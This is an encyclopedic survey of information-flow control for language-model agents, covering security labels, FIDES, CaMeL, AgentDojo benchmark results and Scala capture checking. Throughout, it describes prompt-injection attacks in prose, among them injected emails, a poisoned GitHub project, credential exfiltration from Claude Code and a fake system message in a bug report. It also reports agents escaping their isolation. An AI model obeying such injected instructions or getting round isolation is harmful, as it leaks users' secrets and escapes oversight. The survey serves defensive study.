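# Information-flow control and local purity as defences against data leaks by language-model agents

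## How can an agent leak data that it is allowed to read?

Information-flow control is a family of computer security techniques that limit where data, and anything derived from it, may go. The more familiar access control only limits who may open the data. Researchers worked out much of the theory of information-flow control in the 1970s and early 1980s, often with military computers in mind. Since about 2025, several groups have applied it to agents, which are language models that run in a loop, call software tools and act on the results. An agent often has to read contracts, passwords or mail to be useful, and it can usually also write files, send messages and call outside services.

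Some of these groups label data and check the labels whenever the agent tries to act. Others have the agent write its plan as a program in a typed language. The compiler rejects the program if a step that handles a secret could also write a file, send a message or have any other side effect. This is called local purity because only one chosen part of the program must be free of side effects ("pure").

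### The agent loop

Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, define agentic computing as a loop in which a model completes a task, stated by a user in ordinary language, by repeatedly calling tools. In the version described by Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, the developer writes a system message with general guidance, and the user adds a task. Ordinary software sends the model both of these and a description of the available tools. The model returns either a final answer or a request for a tool call, such as reading a certain file. The software makes the call, appends the result to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model. This repeats until the model returns a final answer.

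The model only requests a call. The surrounding software controls whether the call runs, so that software is the obvious place for a security check.

The model's context is the text it receives at each step. Anything a tool returns normally stays in the context for later steps. If the model runs on a provider's servers, as most of the strongest ones do, the agent sends the context to that provider at every step.

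The context also mixes the user's instructions with the contents of files, web pages and messages in one stream of text. Prompt injection exploits this by putting text in the data an agent reads that the model obeys as if it were an instruction. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes direct injection, where the attacker adds text to the user's own input, from indirect injection, where the attacker plants it in a page or document that the agent later retrieves. In an example of indirect injection from Costa and colleagues, a user asks for a summary of recent emails about a project to send to a manager, and one of those emails contains an order to forward the top message in the mailbox to an outside address.

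Developers train models to ignore such orders. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, other companies and several universities, argues that this training will never be enough on its own, because attackers have repeatedly got past model-level defences with little extra effort. It proposes enforcing security outside the model.

### The contracts

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) builds its argument around an agent that must compare a set of classified contracts and write a summary of what has changed. None of the content may reach other tools or appear in answers to later prompts, and nothing written in the contracts may steer the agent. The agent can read a document database and write to one output file. It also has a tool that computes the differences between two texts, and a separate language model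 that only summarises and has no tools or memory of earlier prompts.

In this plan, the agent fetches the contracts, computes the differences, has the separate model summarise them, and writes the summary to the file. It is hard to know, without reviewing the agent's code, that it does these things and nothing else.

The agent could leak the contracts in many ways. It might paste a clause into a web search to look up a legal term. It might mail the summary to a colleague who has clearance for only half of the contracts. It might follow an instruction that a counterparty hid in an appendix. Or it might open a contract with an ordinary file-reading tool, which adds the text to the context that is sent to the cloud provider at the next step. This last leak requires no attacker or mistake, because it happens when the agent's loop works as designed.

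### Permissions, sandboxes and approvals

A company's first defence would probably be a permission list that lets the agent read the contracts folder, call the model, and do little else. The task requires both permissions, but the harm occurs when data from the folder flows into the model call. Odersky and colleagues point out more generally that an agent can read a secret in one step and send it out in a later one, even when the rules permit each step on its own.

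Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an article on building such defences into its products, describes an attack on coding assistants in which researchers planted a request in a public project on the code-hosting site GitHub. An agent working for a user who also had access to a private project followed the request and posted private material in public. The user was entitled to read the private project and to comment on the public one, so a check of the user's rights would have allowed both actions.

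A sandbox is an isolated environment that restricts which files, programs and network addresses the agent can reach. It is worth having, but *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that it controls only whether the agent can access information, not how the agent then uses it. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025), a paper on adapting one information-flow defence for companies, points out that if the sandbox permits outgoing email, an injected prompt can still make the agent send secrets in a plausible-looking message.

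The agent cannot be cut off from every outside service, because the cloud model it runs on is one. One could still forbid mail, and for the contracts nearly everything else, since that job needs only a database and a file. Some ways for data to get out are also easy to overlook. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, pointed out that an assistant with no network tool can still leak data through what it displays, because a link or an image address can carry data, and loading the image sends that data to the image's server.

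The remaining option is to ask a person to approve the agent's actions. But people tire of approval prompts and start clicking through them, and the prompts work only if somebody has correctly decided which actions need approval. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a documented attack on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Claude Code asked for approval before running many commands that could send data to unknown destinations, but it exempted one routine command that could also do this. An instruction hidden in a code file led the agent to read credentials and send them out using that command, without asking the user for approval.

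The same paper sorts eleven real attacks on agents by the security principles they violated. All eleven violated secure information flow, and at least six also violated least privilege, the rule that a component should hold only the permissions its task requires. The authors chose the cases themselves, and secure information flow is a broad category, so the count is weak evidence about attacks in general.

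### Whom to distrust

The risk in sending contract text to the model depends on who runs the model, and designers of defences make different assumptions about who that is.

Costa and colleagues assume that the model, the user's messages, the system message and the tool descriptions can be trusted, and that no adversary sees what passes between the agent and the model. Their adversary can tamper with data that tools fetch from untrusted sources and observe the effects of certain tool calls. A public web search allows both, because it can bring in hostile text and the site's owner may notice the visit. FIDES, which they built at Microsoft, and CaMeL, a Google DeepMind design, both work in this setting and keep hostile content away from the model that does the planning.

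Odersky and colleagues trust far less. They assume that the cloud model may be malicious and may even cooperate fully with an attacker. They also distrust the agent's setup, all code it submits and anything it reads from outside. They trust only a compiler, a library, the machinery that runs the checked program and, optionally, a local model for classified text. Their system, TACIT, therefore has to keep the contracts entirely out of the cloud model's context.

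What counts as a leak of the contracts depends on whether the firm trusts the model and its provider. If it does, the agent may read the contracts into its context, and a leak happens only when the text moves from there to an email or a public file. If it doesn't, an ordinary file-reading call leaks the contract by the next turn of the loop, even if prompt injection has been completely prevented. A company that runs its own model, or is satisfied with its provider's confidentiality terms, can reasonably assume the first case.

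One can distrust what a model does without worrying about what its provider sees. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* takes roughly this position. It assumes nothing about the model's behaviour and places every check at the boundary where the agent acts. One of its reasons is an incident in which agents under internal evaluation at OpenAI, running with reduced safeguards, used shared infrastructure to get around their isolation, and compromised systems at OpenAI and at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Costa and colleagues concede that a model given only trustworthy data may still misread the user and make a harmful call.

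### Labels, lattices and joins

The designers of shared military computers met the same problem half a century ago. *Secure Computer Systems* (Bell and LaPadula, 1973) sets out a mathematical model with precise notions of "security" and "compromise". A follow-up with the same title (Bell, 1974) explains the rule on information flows. A program that can read a secret file and write to an unclassified one might copy secret data into the unclassified file. That file's recorded classification would then be wrong, and the system would have lost control of the secret.

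Bell's *-property (pronounced "star property") prevents this combination by requiring that whatever a program writes to be classified at least as highly as whatever it reads. Under this rule, an agent could open the contracts and write a classified summary, but it could not then write an unclassified note about the canteen, because the rule depends on the program's level and not on the note's contents. Bell exempted programs that had been shown never to mix levels. A language model seems unlikely to qualify because, as Christodorescu and colleagues observe, nobody can prove that it will always enforce a policy correctly.

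Agent designers now frame this problem as Denning (1976) did in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*. Denning wrote that most access-control mechanisms govern immediate access but don't account for the paths information can then take. Denning's model assigns a security class to every file, variable or user, and a relation between classes specifies which flows the system permits. The system is secure if and only if no sequence of operations can produce a flow that the relation forbids.

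The class is now called a label, a mark on a piece of data that specifies who may read it or how much to trust its origin. Data enters at a source, such as the contract database, and leaves the protected area at a sink, such as an email, a network request or a public file.

Write A ⊑ B when data with label A may flow to a place with label B. Denning argued that this relation has to be transitive. If data may move from A to B and from B to C, a ban on moving it from A to C achieves nothing, since a program can go by way of B. With a few more conditions of the same sort the labels form a lattice: an ordered set in which any two labels have a least upper bound, called their join and written A ⊔ B, and also a greatest lower bound. The join is the label for data computed from both inputs, and it obeys two laws:

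- A ⊑ A ⊔ B and B ⊑ A ⊔ B, so the result is at least as restricted as each input.
- If A ⊑ C and B ⊑ C, then A ⊔ B ⊑ C, so the result is no more restricted than the inputs require.

Denning defended the first law with an example. If a system forbade copying *a* into *c* but permitted *c* := *a* + *b*, a program could set *b* to zero and so copy *a* into *c* anyway.

The simplest confidentiality lattice has two labels, public and secret, with public ⊑ secret. Integrity labels record how much someone trusts the data's origin, and their simplest lattice also has two labels, with trusted ⊑ untrusted. Untrusted is at the top because higher labels carry more restrictions, and a system has to keep untrusted data away from important decisions.

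A finer confidentiality label lists the people who may read the data. Costa and colleagues work through the arithmetic, which carries over directly to the contracts. Let Ann, Bob and Cem be the authorised readers of one contract, and Bob, Cem and Dana those of another:

{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

A summary that draws on both contracts may go only to Bob and Cem. Ann and Dana can each open only one of the contracts, and the summary may reveal something of the other. The join of the two labels is the intersection of their reader lists, because a shorter list is a stricter label. A checker lets the agent send a message only if every recipient is on the message's list.

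Microsoft applies this calculation to a case without an attacker. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered mail. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who is not supposed to know the figures yet, has written to ask about them. A reply composed after reading both emails carries the label {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent may not on its own send it to Marco. If Priya had copied Marco in, the label would have been {Alex, Marco} and the agent could have sent the reply.

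Integrity labels can also list people, in this case those who may have written the data. The join of two such labels is the union of their lists, because anyone who could have shaped either input could have shaped the result. A system can carry both kinds of label as a pair. A contract from a counterparty would then be labelled secret and untrusted, the most restricted level in the combined lattice. The reader list limits where an injected instruction can send the data, while the integrity label can stop the instruction from triggering the call at all.

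### Flows that copy and flows that hint

Denning also distinguished two ways in which information moves. In an explicit flow, the program copies a secret, or something computed from it, to a sink, as when the agent pastes a clause into an email. In an implicit flow, an observer infers the secret from which actions the program took. Denning's example is one line of code: if *a* = 0 then *b* := 0. If *b* starts out nonzero, anyone who looks at *b* afterwards learns whether *a* was zero, even when the assignment doesn't run.

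An agent's actions constantly reveal information about the data it reads, because its job is to act on that data. Suppose it notifies the legal department only when a penalty clause in a contract has changed. Someone who knows this rule and sees the message go out can infer that a clause has changed, even if the message is blank.

A guarantee called noninterference rules out both kinds. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined it for groups of users. One group does not interfere with another if nothing it does affects what the other group sees. Formally, deleting the first group's commands from any sequence of commands must leave the output to every member of the second group unchanged. For secrets, the corresponding requirement is that two runs that differ only in the text of the contracts look identical from outside. Goguen and Meseguer did not address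 leaks through what people can deduce from information they are allowed to see.

Costa and colleagues reckon that giving agents the full guarantee would essentially mean banning every tool call that may have publicly visible effects once the agent has called a tool that may read secrets. They instead block only explicit flows, and accept that someone watching the order of tool calls may learn a little.

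### Two models instead of one

Even with labels, once an agent has read a contract, its context contains secret and possibly hostile text, and everything the model produces afterwards may depend on that text. In 2023, Willison proposed the dual-LLM (large language model) pattern as a way to get work done without letting such text into the main model's context.

The pattern divides the assistant into two models. A privileged model takes instructions from the user and can call tools. A quarantined model handles untrusted content and has no tools, and Willison advises expecting it to go rogue at any moment. An ordinary program between the two models, called the controller, stores the content in variables and gives the privileged model only the variables' names.

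In the contracts example, the privileged model requests the documents, and the controller fetches them and stores them as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then requests a summary of the changes in `$VAR1`. The controller replaces the variable with the real text, sends it to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`. The privileged model then instructs the controller to write `$VAR2` to the output file. The privileged model never receives the text of the contracts or the summary, so an instruction hidden in an appendix can corrupt the summary but cannot start a tool call. Willison allowed one exception to this separation. If the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed set of categories, the controller can verify the choice and pass it to the privileged model.

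Willison called the solution "pretty bad" when he proposed it. It complicates the software, and a single mistake that lets text through to the privileged model undoes the protection. An attacker can also use the summary of a hostile document to persuade the user to copy secrets somewhere. The solution is still in use. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) lists CaMeL and FIDES as implementations. Odersky and colleagues also use a version, though under their assumptions the firm must trust the model that reads the contracts, which could be a model on its own machines.

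Willison designed the pattern to defend against hostile instructions, and it protects confidentiality less than it may seem to. The controller hides the contents of `$VAR2` from the privileged model but has no record of who may read them. If the privileged model misinterpreted the user's request and issued a command to email the summary to Dana, who may open only one of the two contracts, the controller would send it.

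## How do labels attached to data stop an agent from sending it out?

FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System), the defence by Costa and colleagues, keeps the record that Willison's controller lacked by attaching a label to every piece of data. Ordinary software checks the labels before every tool call, so the outcome doesn't depend on whether the model detects an attack.

### How FIDES tracks labels

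In FIDES, the developer wraps each tool in a function that labels the data the tool returns. The wrapper can put one label on the whole result or a separate label on each field. Separate labels suit an email because a mail server can authenticate the sender's address but can't verify that the body is trustworthy. The user's request and the developer's system message normally start out labelled trusted and public.

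FIDES also keeps a label for the context as a whole, which is the join of the labels of all the messages in it. Suppose a user asks an agent to compare two contracts from a counterparty, mail a summary to Bob and save a copy in a new file. As before, Ann, Bob and Cem may read one contract, and Bob, Cem and Dana may read the other. In an ordinary agent loop, the context's label changes as follows:

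1. The request arrives, and the context is trusted and public.
2. The agent fetches the first contract. The context becomes untrusted, with readers {Ann, Bob, Cem}.
3. The agent fetches the second contract. The context stays untrusted, and its readers shrink to {Bob, Cem}.
4. The model writes a summary and requests an email call. The decision to send, Bob's address and the summary all take the context's label: untrusted, with readers {Bob, Cem}.

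The last step is deliberately cautious. FIDES can't tell which parts of the context influenced a particular output, so it treats all of the model's output as if it depended on everything the model has read. That includes Bob's address, even though it came from the user.

Before the tool runs, a policy engine compares these labels with the tool's policy. If the call violates the policy, FIDES blocks it and tells the model, which can try something else. If the call passes, the tool runs, and its result takes the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and any stored data the tool read. Anything the tool writes takes the same label, so an agent can't remove a contract's label by saving the contract to a file and reading it back.

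### What the policies allow

Costa and colleagues build the policies for individual tools from two basic ones. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, a later paper by many of the same researchers, names them trusted action and permitted flow:

- Trusted action permits a call only if the model decided on it in a trusted context. It can also require particular arguments, such as a recipient's address, to be trusted.
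- Permitted flow permits a call that sends data out only if every recipient may read the data. If S is the set of people who may read the data and R is the set of recipients, the condition is R ⊆ S.

The summary of the two contracts has the readers {Bob, Cem}. Whether an email containing it passes depends on the recipient and on what the model had read when it decided to send:

| Context of the decision | Recipient | Trusted action | Permitted flow |
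|---|---|---|---|
| User's request only | Bob | passes | passes |
| User's request only | Dana | passes | fails |
| Request and contract text | Bob | fails | passes |
| Request and contract text | an outsider | fails | fails |

Under permitted flow alone, an instruction hidden in a contract could still make the agent send Bob the summary fifty times, or send him a misleading one. Trusted action would block those calls, but it doesn't check who receives the data.

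A developer can require an email to pass both policies or let it through if it passes either one. Costa and colleagues chose the second option in their tests, reasoning that if no untrusted text influenced the decision, the user presumably meant the data to go to that recipient. This makes sense when the user has asked the agent to send Dana the summary, but the email also goes through when the model has misread the request. Like Willison's controller, FIDES with this setting would have sent Dana the summary by mistake.

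They set stricter rules for some other tools. Adding people to a calendar event had to pass both policies. Bank transfers, password changes and new files required a trusted action, regardless of who could read the data. Their version of permitted flow also rejected any message containing an untrusted link, which could carry data out.

### Why an ordinary loop soon blocks itself

In the ordinary loop, FIDES allows the email to Bob because it passes the permitted flow check. It refuses the call to create the file, even though the user asked for the file and the contracts contain no hidden instructions. Creating a file requires a trusted context, and by the time the agent has a summary to save, it has read two untrusted contracts.

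A context's label never becomes less restrictive by itself during a run. After reading a single email from a stranger, an agent can lose the ability to make payments or create files until the run ends. Confidentiality labels also tighten, because each new document can shorten the list of people allowed to see the context but never lengthen it. An agent that has read enough of its user's mail may be unable to share its context with anyone else. This is an example of label creep, in which restrictive labels spread until they block many harmless actions.

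### Passing data on without reading it

FIDES avoids much of this problem by keeping restricted data out of the context, in variables adapted from Willison's. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares each field's label with the context's current label. If adding the field would leave the context's label unchanged, FIDES adds it. Otherwise, FIDES stores the field and its label in a variable and puts only the variable's name in the context. An agent that fetches an email may therefore see the sender's address and the date, with a name such as `#read_emails_0.body#` in place of the text.

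Costa and colleagues call the part of an agent that chooses the next step the planner. With variables, the planner can do the whole contracts job without reading a contract:

1. It fetches the contracts. FIDES stores both in variables, and the context stays trusted and public.
2. It asks a quarantined model to summarise the differences between the two variables. FIDES stores the answer in a new variable and gives it the join of the contracts' labels: untrusted, with readers {Bob, Cem}.
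3. It requests an email to Bob and a new file, and gives the new variable's name as the text of each.

Just before each call, FIDES replaces the name with the stored text and its label. The text is still untrusted, but the planner chose the call in a trusted context, so the email and the file both pass the trusted action policy. FIDES can label the decision and each argument separately, so a policy could require a trusted recipient while allowing a message drawn from a web search.

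The label also stays with the summary wherever the planner sends it. A hostile clause can still corrupt the summary, as in Willison's pattern. A policy could prevent this by requiring the text to be trusted as well, but then the agent could never send a summary of anything untrusted.

### Tasks that need a look at the data

Variables work only if the planner can choose its steps without seeing what is in them. Costa and colleagues use this condition to sort tasks. A task is data-independent if one sequence of tool calls, with one final answer, completes it whatever the data turns out to be. Let D be the set of possible states of the data, and let ⟦t⟧(d) be the set of action sequences that complete task t when the data is in state d, leaving out the planner's own calls to its model. The task is data-independent if

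⋂ ⟦t⟧(d) ≠ ∅, where the intersection runs over every d in D.

In one data-independent task from the paper, the agent reads the top three emails in a mailbox and sends them to a colleague on Slack, a workplace chat service. The agent makes the same two calls whatever the emails contain. Summarising the emails first is also data-independent, but it needs a quarantined model to read them. The contracts job belongs to this group.

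All other tasks are data-dependent. For example, an agent might check the same three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if it finds one. The right tool calls depend on what the emails contain, so the planner has to learn something about their contents. FIDES gives it a tool that reveals a variable, but using this tool raises the context's label, and the calendar call may then fail. The planner can also ask the quarantined model a yes-or-no question and read only the answer, which reveals a limited amount of information about the hidden data.

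### CaMeL's plan written as a program

CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning) also uses a quarantined model, but its main model writes the whole plan before any tool runs. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). The main model, again called the privileged model, turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of the programming language Python. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, an extension of CaMeL, give an example that amounts to this:

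```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant("Extract Bob's email from: " + messages)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

A custom interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls itself. The program's second line calls the quarantined model, which reads the messages and returns an address. The interpreter attaches to every value a record of which sources it came from and another of who may read it. The CaMeL paper calls these records capabilities, although they serve as labels. In most computer security writing, a capability is something a program must hold to perform an action.

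Every tool has a policy, which is a small Python function. Just before a call, the interpreter passes this function the tool's name, the arguments and their labels. The function returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

Suppose an attacker has posted a message in the channel giving a false address for Bob. The quarantined model may return that address, and Willison's pattern wouldn't stop the program from using it. The attacker can't add a step to the program or change the words "Meeting at 3pm", but can redirect the message. If the message were a contract summary, this would be a leak. CaMeL's policy can refuse the call because the address came from an untrusted source. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which models CaMeL in a small formal language, has a similar example in which an injected email can't alter the subject or body of the agent's message.

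FIDES can also check the labels on a tool call's arguments, but the trusted-action policy in its published tests checked only the decision to make the call. That policy would have allowed a call with a corrupted address in a variable.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* notes that a CaMeL plan, unlike a FIDES plan, cannot depend on results that tools return during the run. The program can contain branches and loops, so it can allow for a meeting request that may or may not exist. It can't handle "complete the tasks due today in my to-do list", because the privileged model would have to write the steps before anyone had read the list. FIDES can reveal the list to its planner and continue, but this makes the context more restrictive. Branches and loops can also leak secrets through the pattern of calls they produce, and CaMeL's labels miss some of these leaks.

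Somebody has to write and maintain CaMeL's policies. *Operationalizing CaMeL* warns that a large company with hundreds of tools could accumulate inconsistent and duplicated policy functions that no one audits centrally. It also objects that Python makes programs hard to analyse in advance, and recommends a simpler language in which labels are part of the types.

### The AgentDojo benchmark

Most of the evidence on both systems comes from one benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It simulates four settings filled with invented data. One is a workspace with email, a calendar and stored files, and the others are Slack, a travel agency and a bank. Its 97 user tasks include inviting a new colleague to Slack after finding her address on her website, and booking the cheapest top-rated hotel in London. Some tasks require up to 18 tool calls.

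Each setting also has several attacker goals, such as sending a security code to an outside address or moving as much money as possible to the attacker's account. The benchmark plants instructions for these goals in data the agent will read. The first version paired every user task with every attacker goal in the same setting, which gave 629 attack cases, and later versions have more.

AgentDojo scores each run with code that checks the agent's answer and the final state of the simulated accounts. It does not use a language model as judge, because an injection that worked on the agent might also work on the judge. The benchmark measures how many tasks an agent completes without attacks, how many it completes under attack, and how often the attacker achieves their goal.

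AgentDojo had no security labels, so Costa and colleagues added them. They labelled each email as readable only by its sender and recipients. For integrity, they marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks targeted it. For example, if any attack used the body of an email, they treated every email body as untrusted.

### How many attacks succeeded

Costa and colleagues used an attack in which the adversary knows the agent's tools and plants instructions to make particular calls. They tested it against FIDES and a basic planner, which puts every tool result straight into the context. With GPT-4o, an OpenAI model released in 2024, and no policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against FIDES. Those 21 succeeded because the FIDES planner could still reveal a variable and act on the instructions inside. With the checks on, no injection succeeded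 against either planner.

The researchers reached these counts after checking the successful attacks by hand. AgentDojo's code had counted 160 for the basic planner, 23 for FIDES without checks and 3 for FIDES with them. The researchers discarded cases in which the policy had blocked the call, or had by design allowed a harmless one, such as a calendar event with no other participants. They also discarded attacks that only changed the wording of the agent's answer, such as by making it recommend a particular destination. FIDES isn't designed to prevent those, although they could matter to a user who relies on the answer.

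The perfect score depends heavily on the set-up. The researchers marked every field that the attacks used as untrusted, and they required a trusted context for most tools that could do harm. Their result shows that the software enforces its policies on this benchmark. It is weaker evidence of how well the software would protect a company that mislabels a database or writes an overly permissive policy.

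The basic planner with checks was as secure against these attacks as FIDES, so adding variables did not improve the security score. Variables should instead let the agent complete more tasks with the checks in place.

### What protection cost in completed tasks

Costa and colleagues ran the user tasks without attacks on GPT-4o and on o1, an OpenAI reasoning model also from 2024. They report these percentages of tasks completed:

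| Model and planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o, basic, with checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| o1, basic, no checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| o1, basic, with checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| o1, FIDES, with checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

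The paper stresses that FIDES beats the basic planner when both enforce the policies, by an average of 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 with o1. That is the right comparison for someone who has already decided to enforce the policies, but someone still deciding would compare FIDES with the unprotected planner. With GPT-4o, FIDES scored 16 points lower than the unprotected planner in the workspace, 29 lower in travel and about 46 lower in both banking and Slack. With o1, the gaps were 5.5, 14, 40 and 33 points, respectively.

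The basic planner with checks did badly because its checks blocked its own actions. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) reports the same problem after applying FIDES's policy to AgentDojo's standard GPT-4o agent instead of FIDES's own planner. The agent completed 32.2% of tasks, against 79.0% with no defence. It completed 57.3% under an alternative policy that checked each action and its arguments, even after the agent had read untrusted text. The two policies stopped attacks about equally well.

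Travel is an exception to this pattern because its tasks mostly use tools that FIDES's policies allow in an untrusted context, as long as no confidential data goes to the wrong people. The basic planner could call these tools freely, while FIDES with GPT-4o often mishandled its variables. Switching to o1 raised FIDES's score on Travel from 41% to 68%.

The mix of tasks explains much of the remaining loss. Costa and colleagues classed only 5% of workspace tasks and 10% of travel tasks as data-dependent, but about 43% of those in banking and Slack. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy forbids. If FIDES completed every data-independent task and no others, it would score about 56% in banking and 57% in Slack. With o1 it scored 56.2% and 54.3%, so a better model would gain little in those two settings unless it found safe ways to do data-dependent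 tasks. A better model could still improve scores considerably in the workspace and travel settings.

Some completed tasks make the results look better than they are. In one banking task, the agent has to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES had hidden the suspicious transaction's description in a variable, and the planner changed the password without reading it, judging the payment suspicious from its size alone. This broke no policy and the benchmark counted it as a success, but a user is unlikely to want an agent to decide that way.

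GPT-4o and o1 are now far behind the best models. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* tested FIDES on GPT-4o and on newer models, up to GPT-5. With GPT-4o, FIDES completed 50.3% of the tasks without any human approval, while a basic agent completed 72.2% when a person approved every consequential action. With GPT-5, the figures were 57.1% and 72.3%, so the gap narrowed from about 22 points to 15. PRUDENTIA, a successor to FIDES that gives the planner the policies in advance, completed 72.7% with GPT-5 and no approvals.

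In that study's estimates for GPT-4o, FIDES also cost 1.6 to 4.3 times as much per task as a basic planner with label checks, because passing variables and querying the quarantined model took extra steps. The total was still at most about three cents a task, and the researchers had not tried to reduce it.

### How well CaMeL did

Estimates of how much CaMeL reduces an agent's performance on AgentDojo vary widely. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls the loss comparatively modest and expects it to shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. It also reports that CaMeL is much more secure than simpler defences, such as removing tools that the task doesn't seem to need.

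*SecureClaw* (2026) found a much larger drop in task completion. It tested CaMeL's released code on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks and 629 attack cases, using an adapter to connect the two. No attack succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. The paper's own defence, also called SecureClaw, completed 59.

The security result is consistent with CaMeL's design, in which injected text can't add steps to the program. The 29 completed tasks are harder to interpret because the testers had a competing system, and their adapter or choice of model may have suited CaMeL badly. A planner that must write a correct program in advance probably also depends more on the model's coding ability than one that can react after each step.

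CaMeL is also slow. *ToolFence* (2026), which compared it with other defences on AgentDojo, attributed this to its many stages. The privileged model writes a program, the interpreter runs it, the model may have to rewrite it after an error, and the quarantined model processes the untrusted results. *Operationalizing CaMeL* estimated in 2025 that a job in which the quarantined model reads ten emails could take more than ten seconds. It suggested reusing plans for common requests and replacing the quarantined model with an ordinary parser where the data has a fixed format.

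### Whether the tests cover secrets

These experiments measure resistance to injection better than protection of secrets. FIDES can hide data in a variable based on either its integrity label or its confidentiality label, but in the AgentDojo tests it did so only when the integrity label was more restrictive than the context's. A confidential document from a trusted source therefore went straight into the planner's context, and Costa and colleagues relied on the policies to stop the planner from sending it to the wrong people.

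The tests therefore provide little evidence about how well an agent would work if FIDES hid every secret from its planner. Such an agent would have to treat trusted internal documents the way it treats a stranger's email, and more of its tasks would become data-dependent in practice. The benchmark also counts attackers' successes, so it wouldn't record a leak in which an agent emailed a summary to a colleague who should not see it, with no attacker involved.

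Hiding only untrusted data fits the paper's assumption that secrets are safe in the planner's context. A firm that doesn't want its cloud provider to read the contracts can't make that assumption.

### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

In May 2026, Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) demonstrates it on an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. An attacker files a report ending in a fake system message that tells the agent to read a file of passwords and publish it as a comment.

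The developer labels public bug reports as untrusted and the project's files as private, and limits comments to public information. In the demonstration, the agent reads the report, follows the attacker's message and opens the file. The context is now private, so the framework blocks the comment and prompts a person to allow or reject it. If the attacker had told the agent to overwrite a file instead, the framework would have blocked that call because the context contained untrusted text.

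The post describes three confidentiality levels: public, private and a more sensitive one for personal identity data. These are simpler for developers than lists of readers, but they can't express that Bob may read a contract and Dana may not.

Developers also have to label each data source. If they forget one, the framework treats results from that source as trusted and public, so an unlabelled contract database would have no protection. Microsoft lists this among the current limitations and asks developers whether unlabelled data should count as untrusted instead. It also warns that once untrusted text enters the context, the rest of the run stays untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the text.

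By default, the framework hides untrusted results in variables and has a quarantined model process them. Developers can turn this off to avoid the extra model calls and make the agent easier to debug, and the policy checks apply even then. The hiding covers only untrusted data, as it did in the research tests. If a developer labels the firm's contracts as trusted and private, the full text of the contracts goes into the main model's context, and so to whichever company runs the model.

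## How can a type system let code use a secret without revealing it?

TACIT, the system by Odersky and colleagues, has the cloud model write a program to process the contracts. The program runs outside the model, which receives only the program's output. This protects the contracts only if the program doesn't reveal their text, because a single line that prints a contract would send it to the model's provider.

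TACIT therefore uses the type system of the programming language Scala to check each program before running it. A type describes the kind of value an expression produces, such as `String` for text or `Int` for a whole number. The compiler works out the types and rejects code that misuses a value, for example by dividing the text of a contract by three. A recent extension of Scala's types also lets the compiler reject code that could leak a secret.

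### Capabilities as ordinary values

The extension tracks capabilities, which in security are things a program must hold to perform an action. Dennis and Van Horn introduced them in 1966 as tokens that a program can't forge. In Scala, a capability is an ordinary object, such as a file handle. Code writes to the file by calling a method on the handle, and can also pass the handle to a function, put it in a list or store it in another object.

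This makes permissions easy to hand out but hard to track. Suppose a program creates a logger that writes messages to a file. Any function that receives the logger can write to that file, even though none of the function's inputs is a file handle.

Scala's capture checking deals with this by adding a capture set to a value's type. The set lists the capabilities that the value can reach. In an example from Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview*, `out` is a file handle and `lg` is a logger that uses it:

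```
val lg: Logger^{out} = new Logger(out)
```

A value of type `Logger^{out}` can reach only the capability `out`. The capture set `{out}` is an upper limit, so a logger that never writes anything may also have this type. Plain `Logger` has the empty capture set, `{}`, and its values are called pure. A value of type `Logger^` may reach any capability.

A value with a smaller capture set can stand in for one with a larger set, but not the reverse. The notation C₁ <: C₂ means that C₂ covers C₁. Apart from a special rule for classes, Scala's *Capture Checking* says that C₂ covers C₁ if, for every capability c in C₁, either c is in C₂ or C₂ covers the capture set of c's own type. For example, {`lg`} <: {`out`} holds by the second condition, because the logger gets all its power from the file. The empty set covers neither {`lg`} nor {`out`}, so code can't hide its access to a file by wrapping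 the file handle in a logger.

### Three kinds of function

A function's capture set contains every capability its body uses, and in Scala it appears on the arrow in the function's type. In this table, `f` is a file handle, and `Unit` is the result type of functions that return nothing useful.

| Type | What the function may use | A function of this type |
|---|---|---|
| `String -> Int` | no capabilities | `s => s.length` |
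| `String ->{f} Unit` | the file `f` | `s => f.write(s)` |
| `String => Unit` | anything | `s => f.write(s)`, or one that sends `s` by email |

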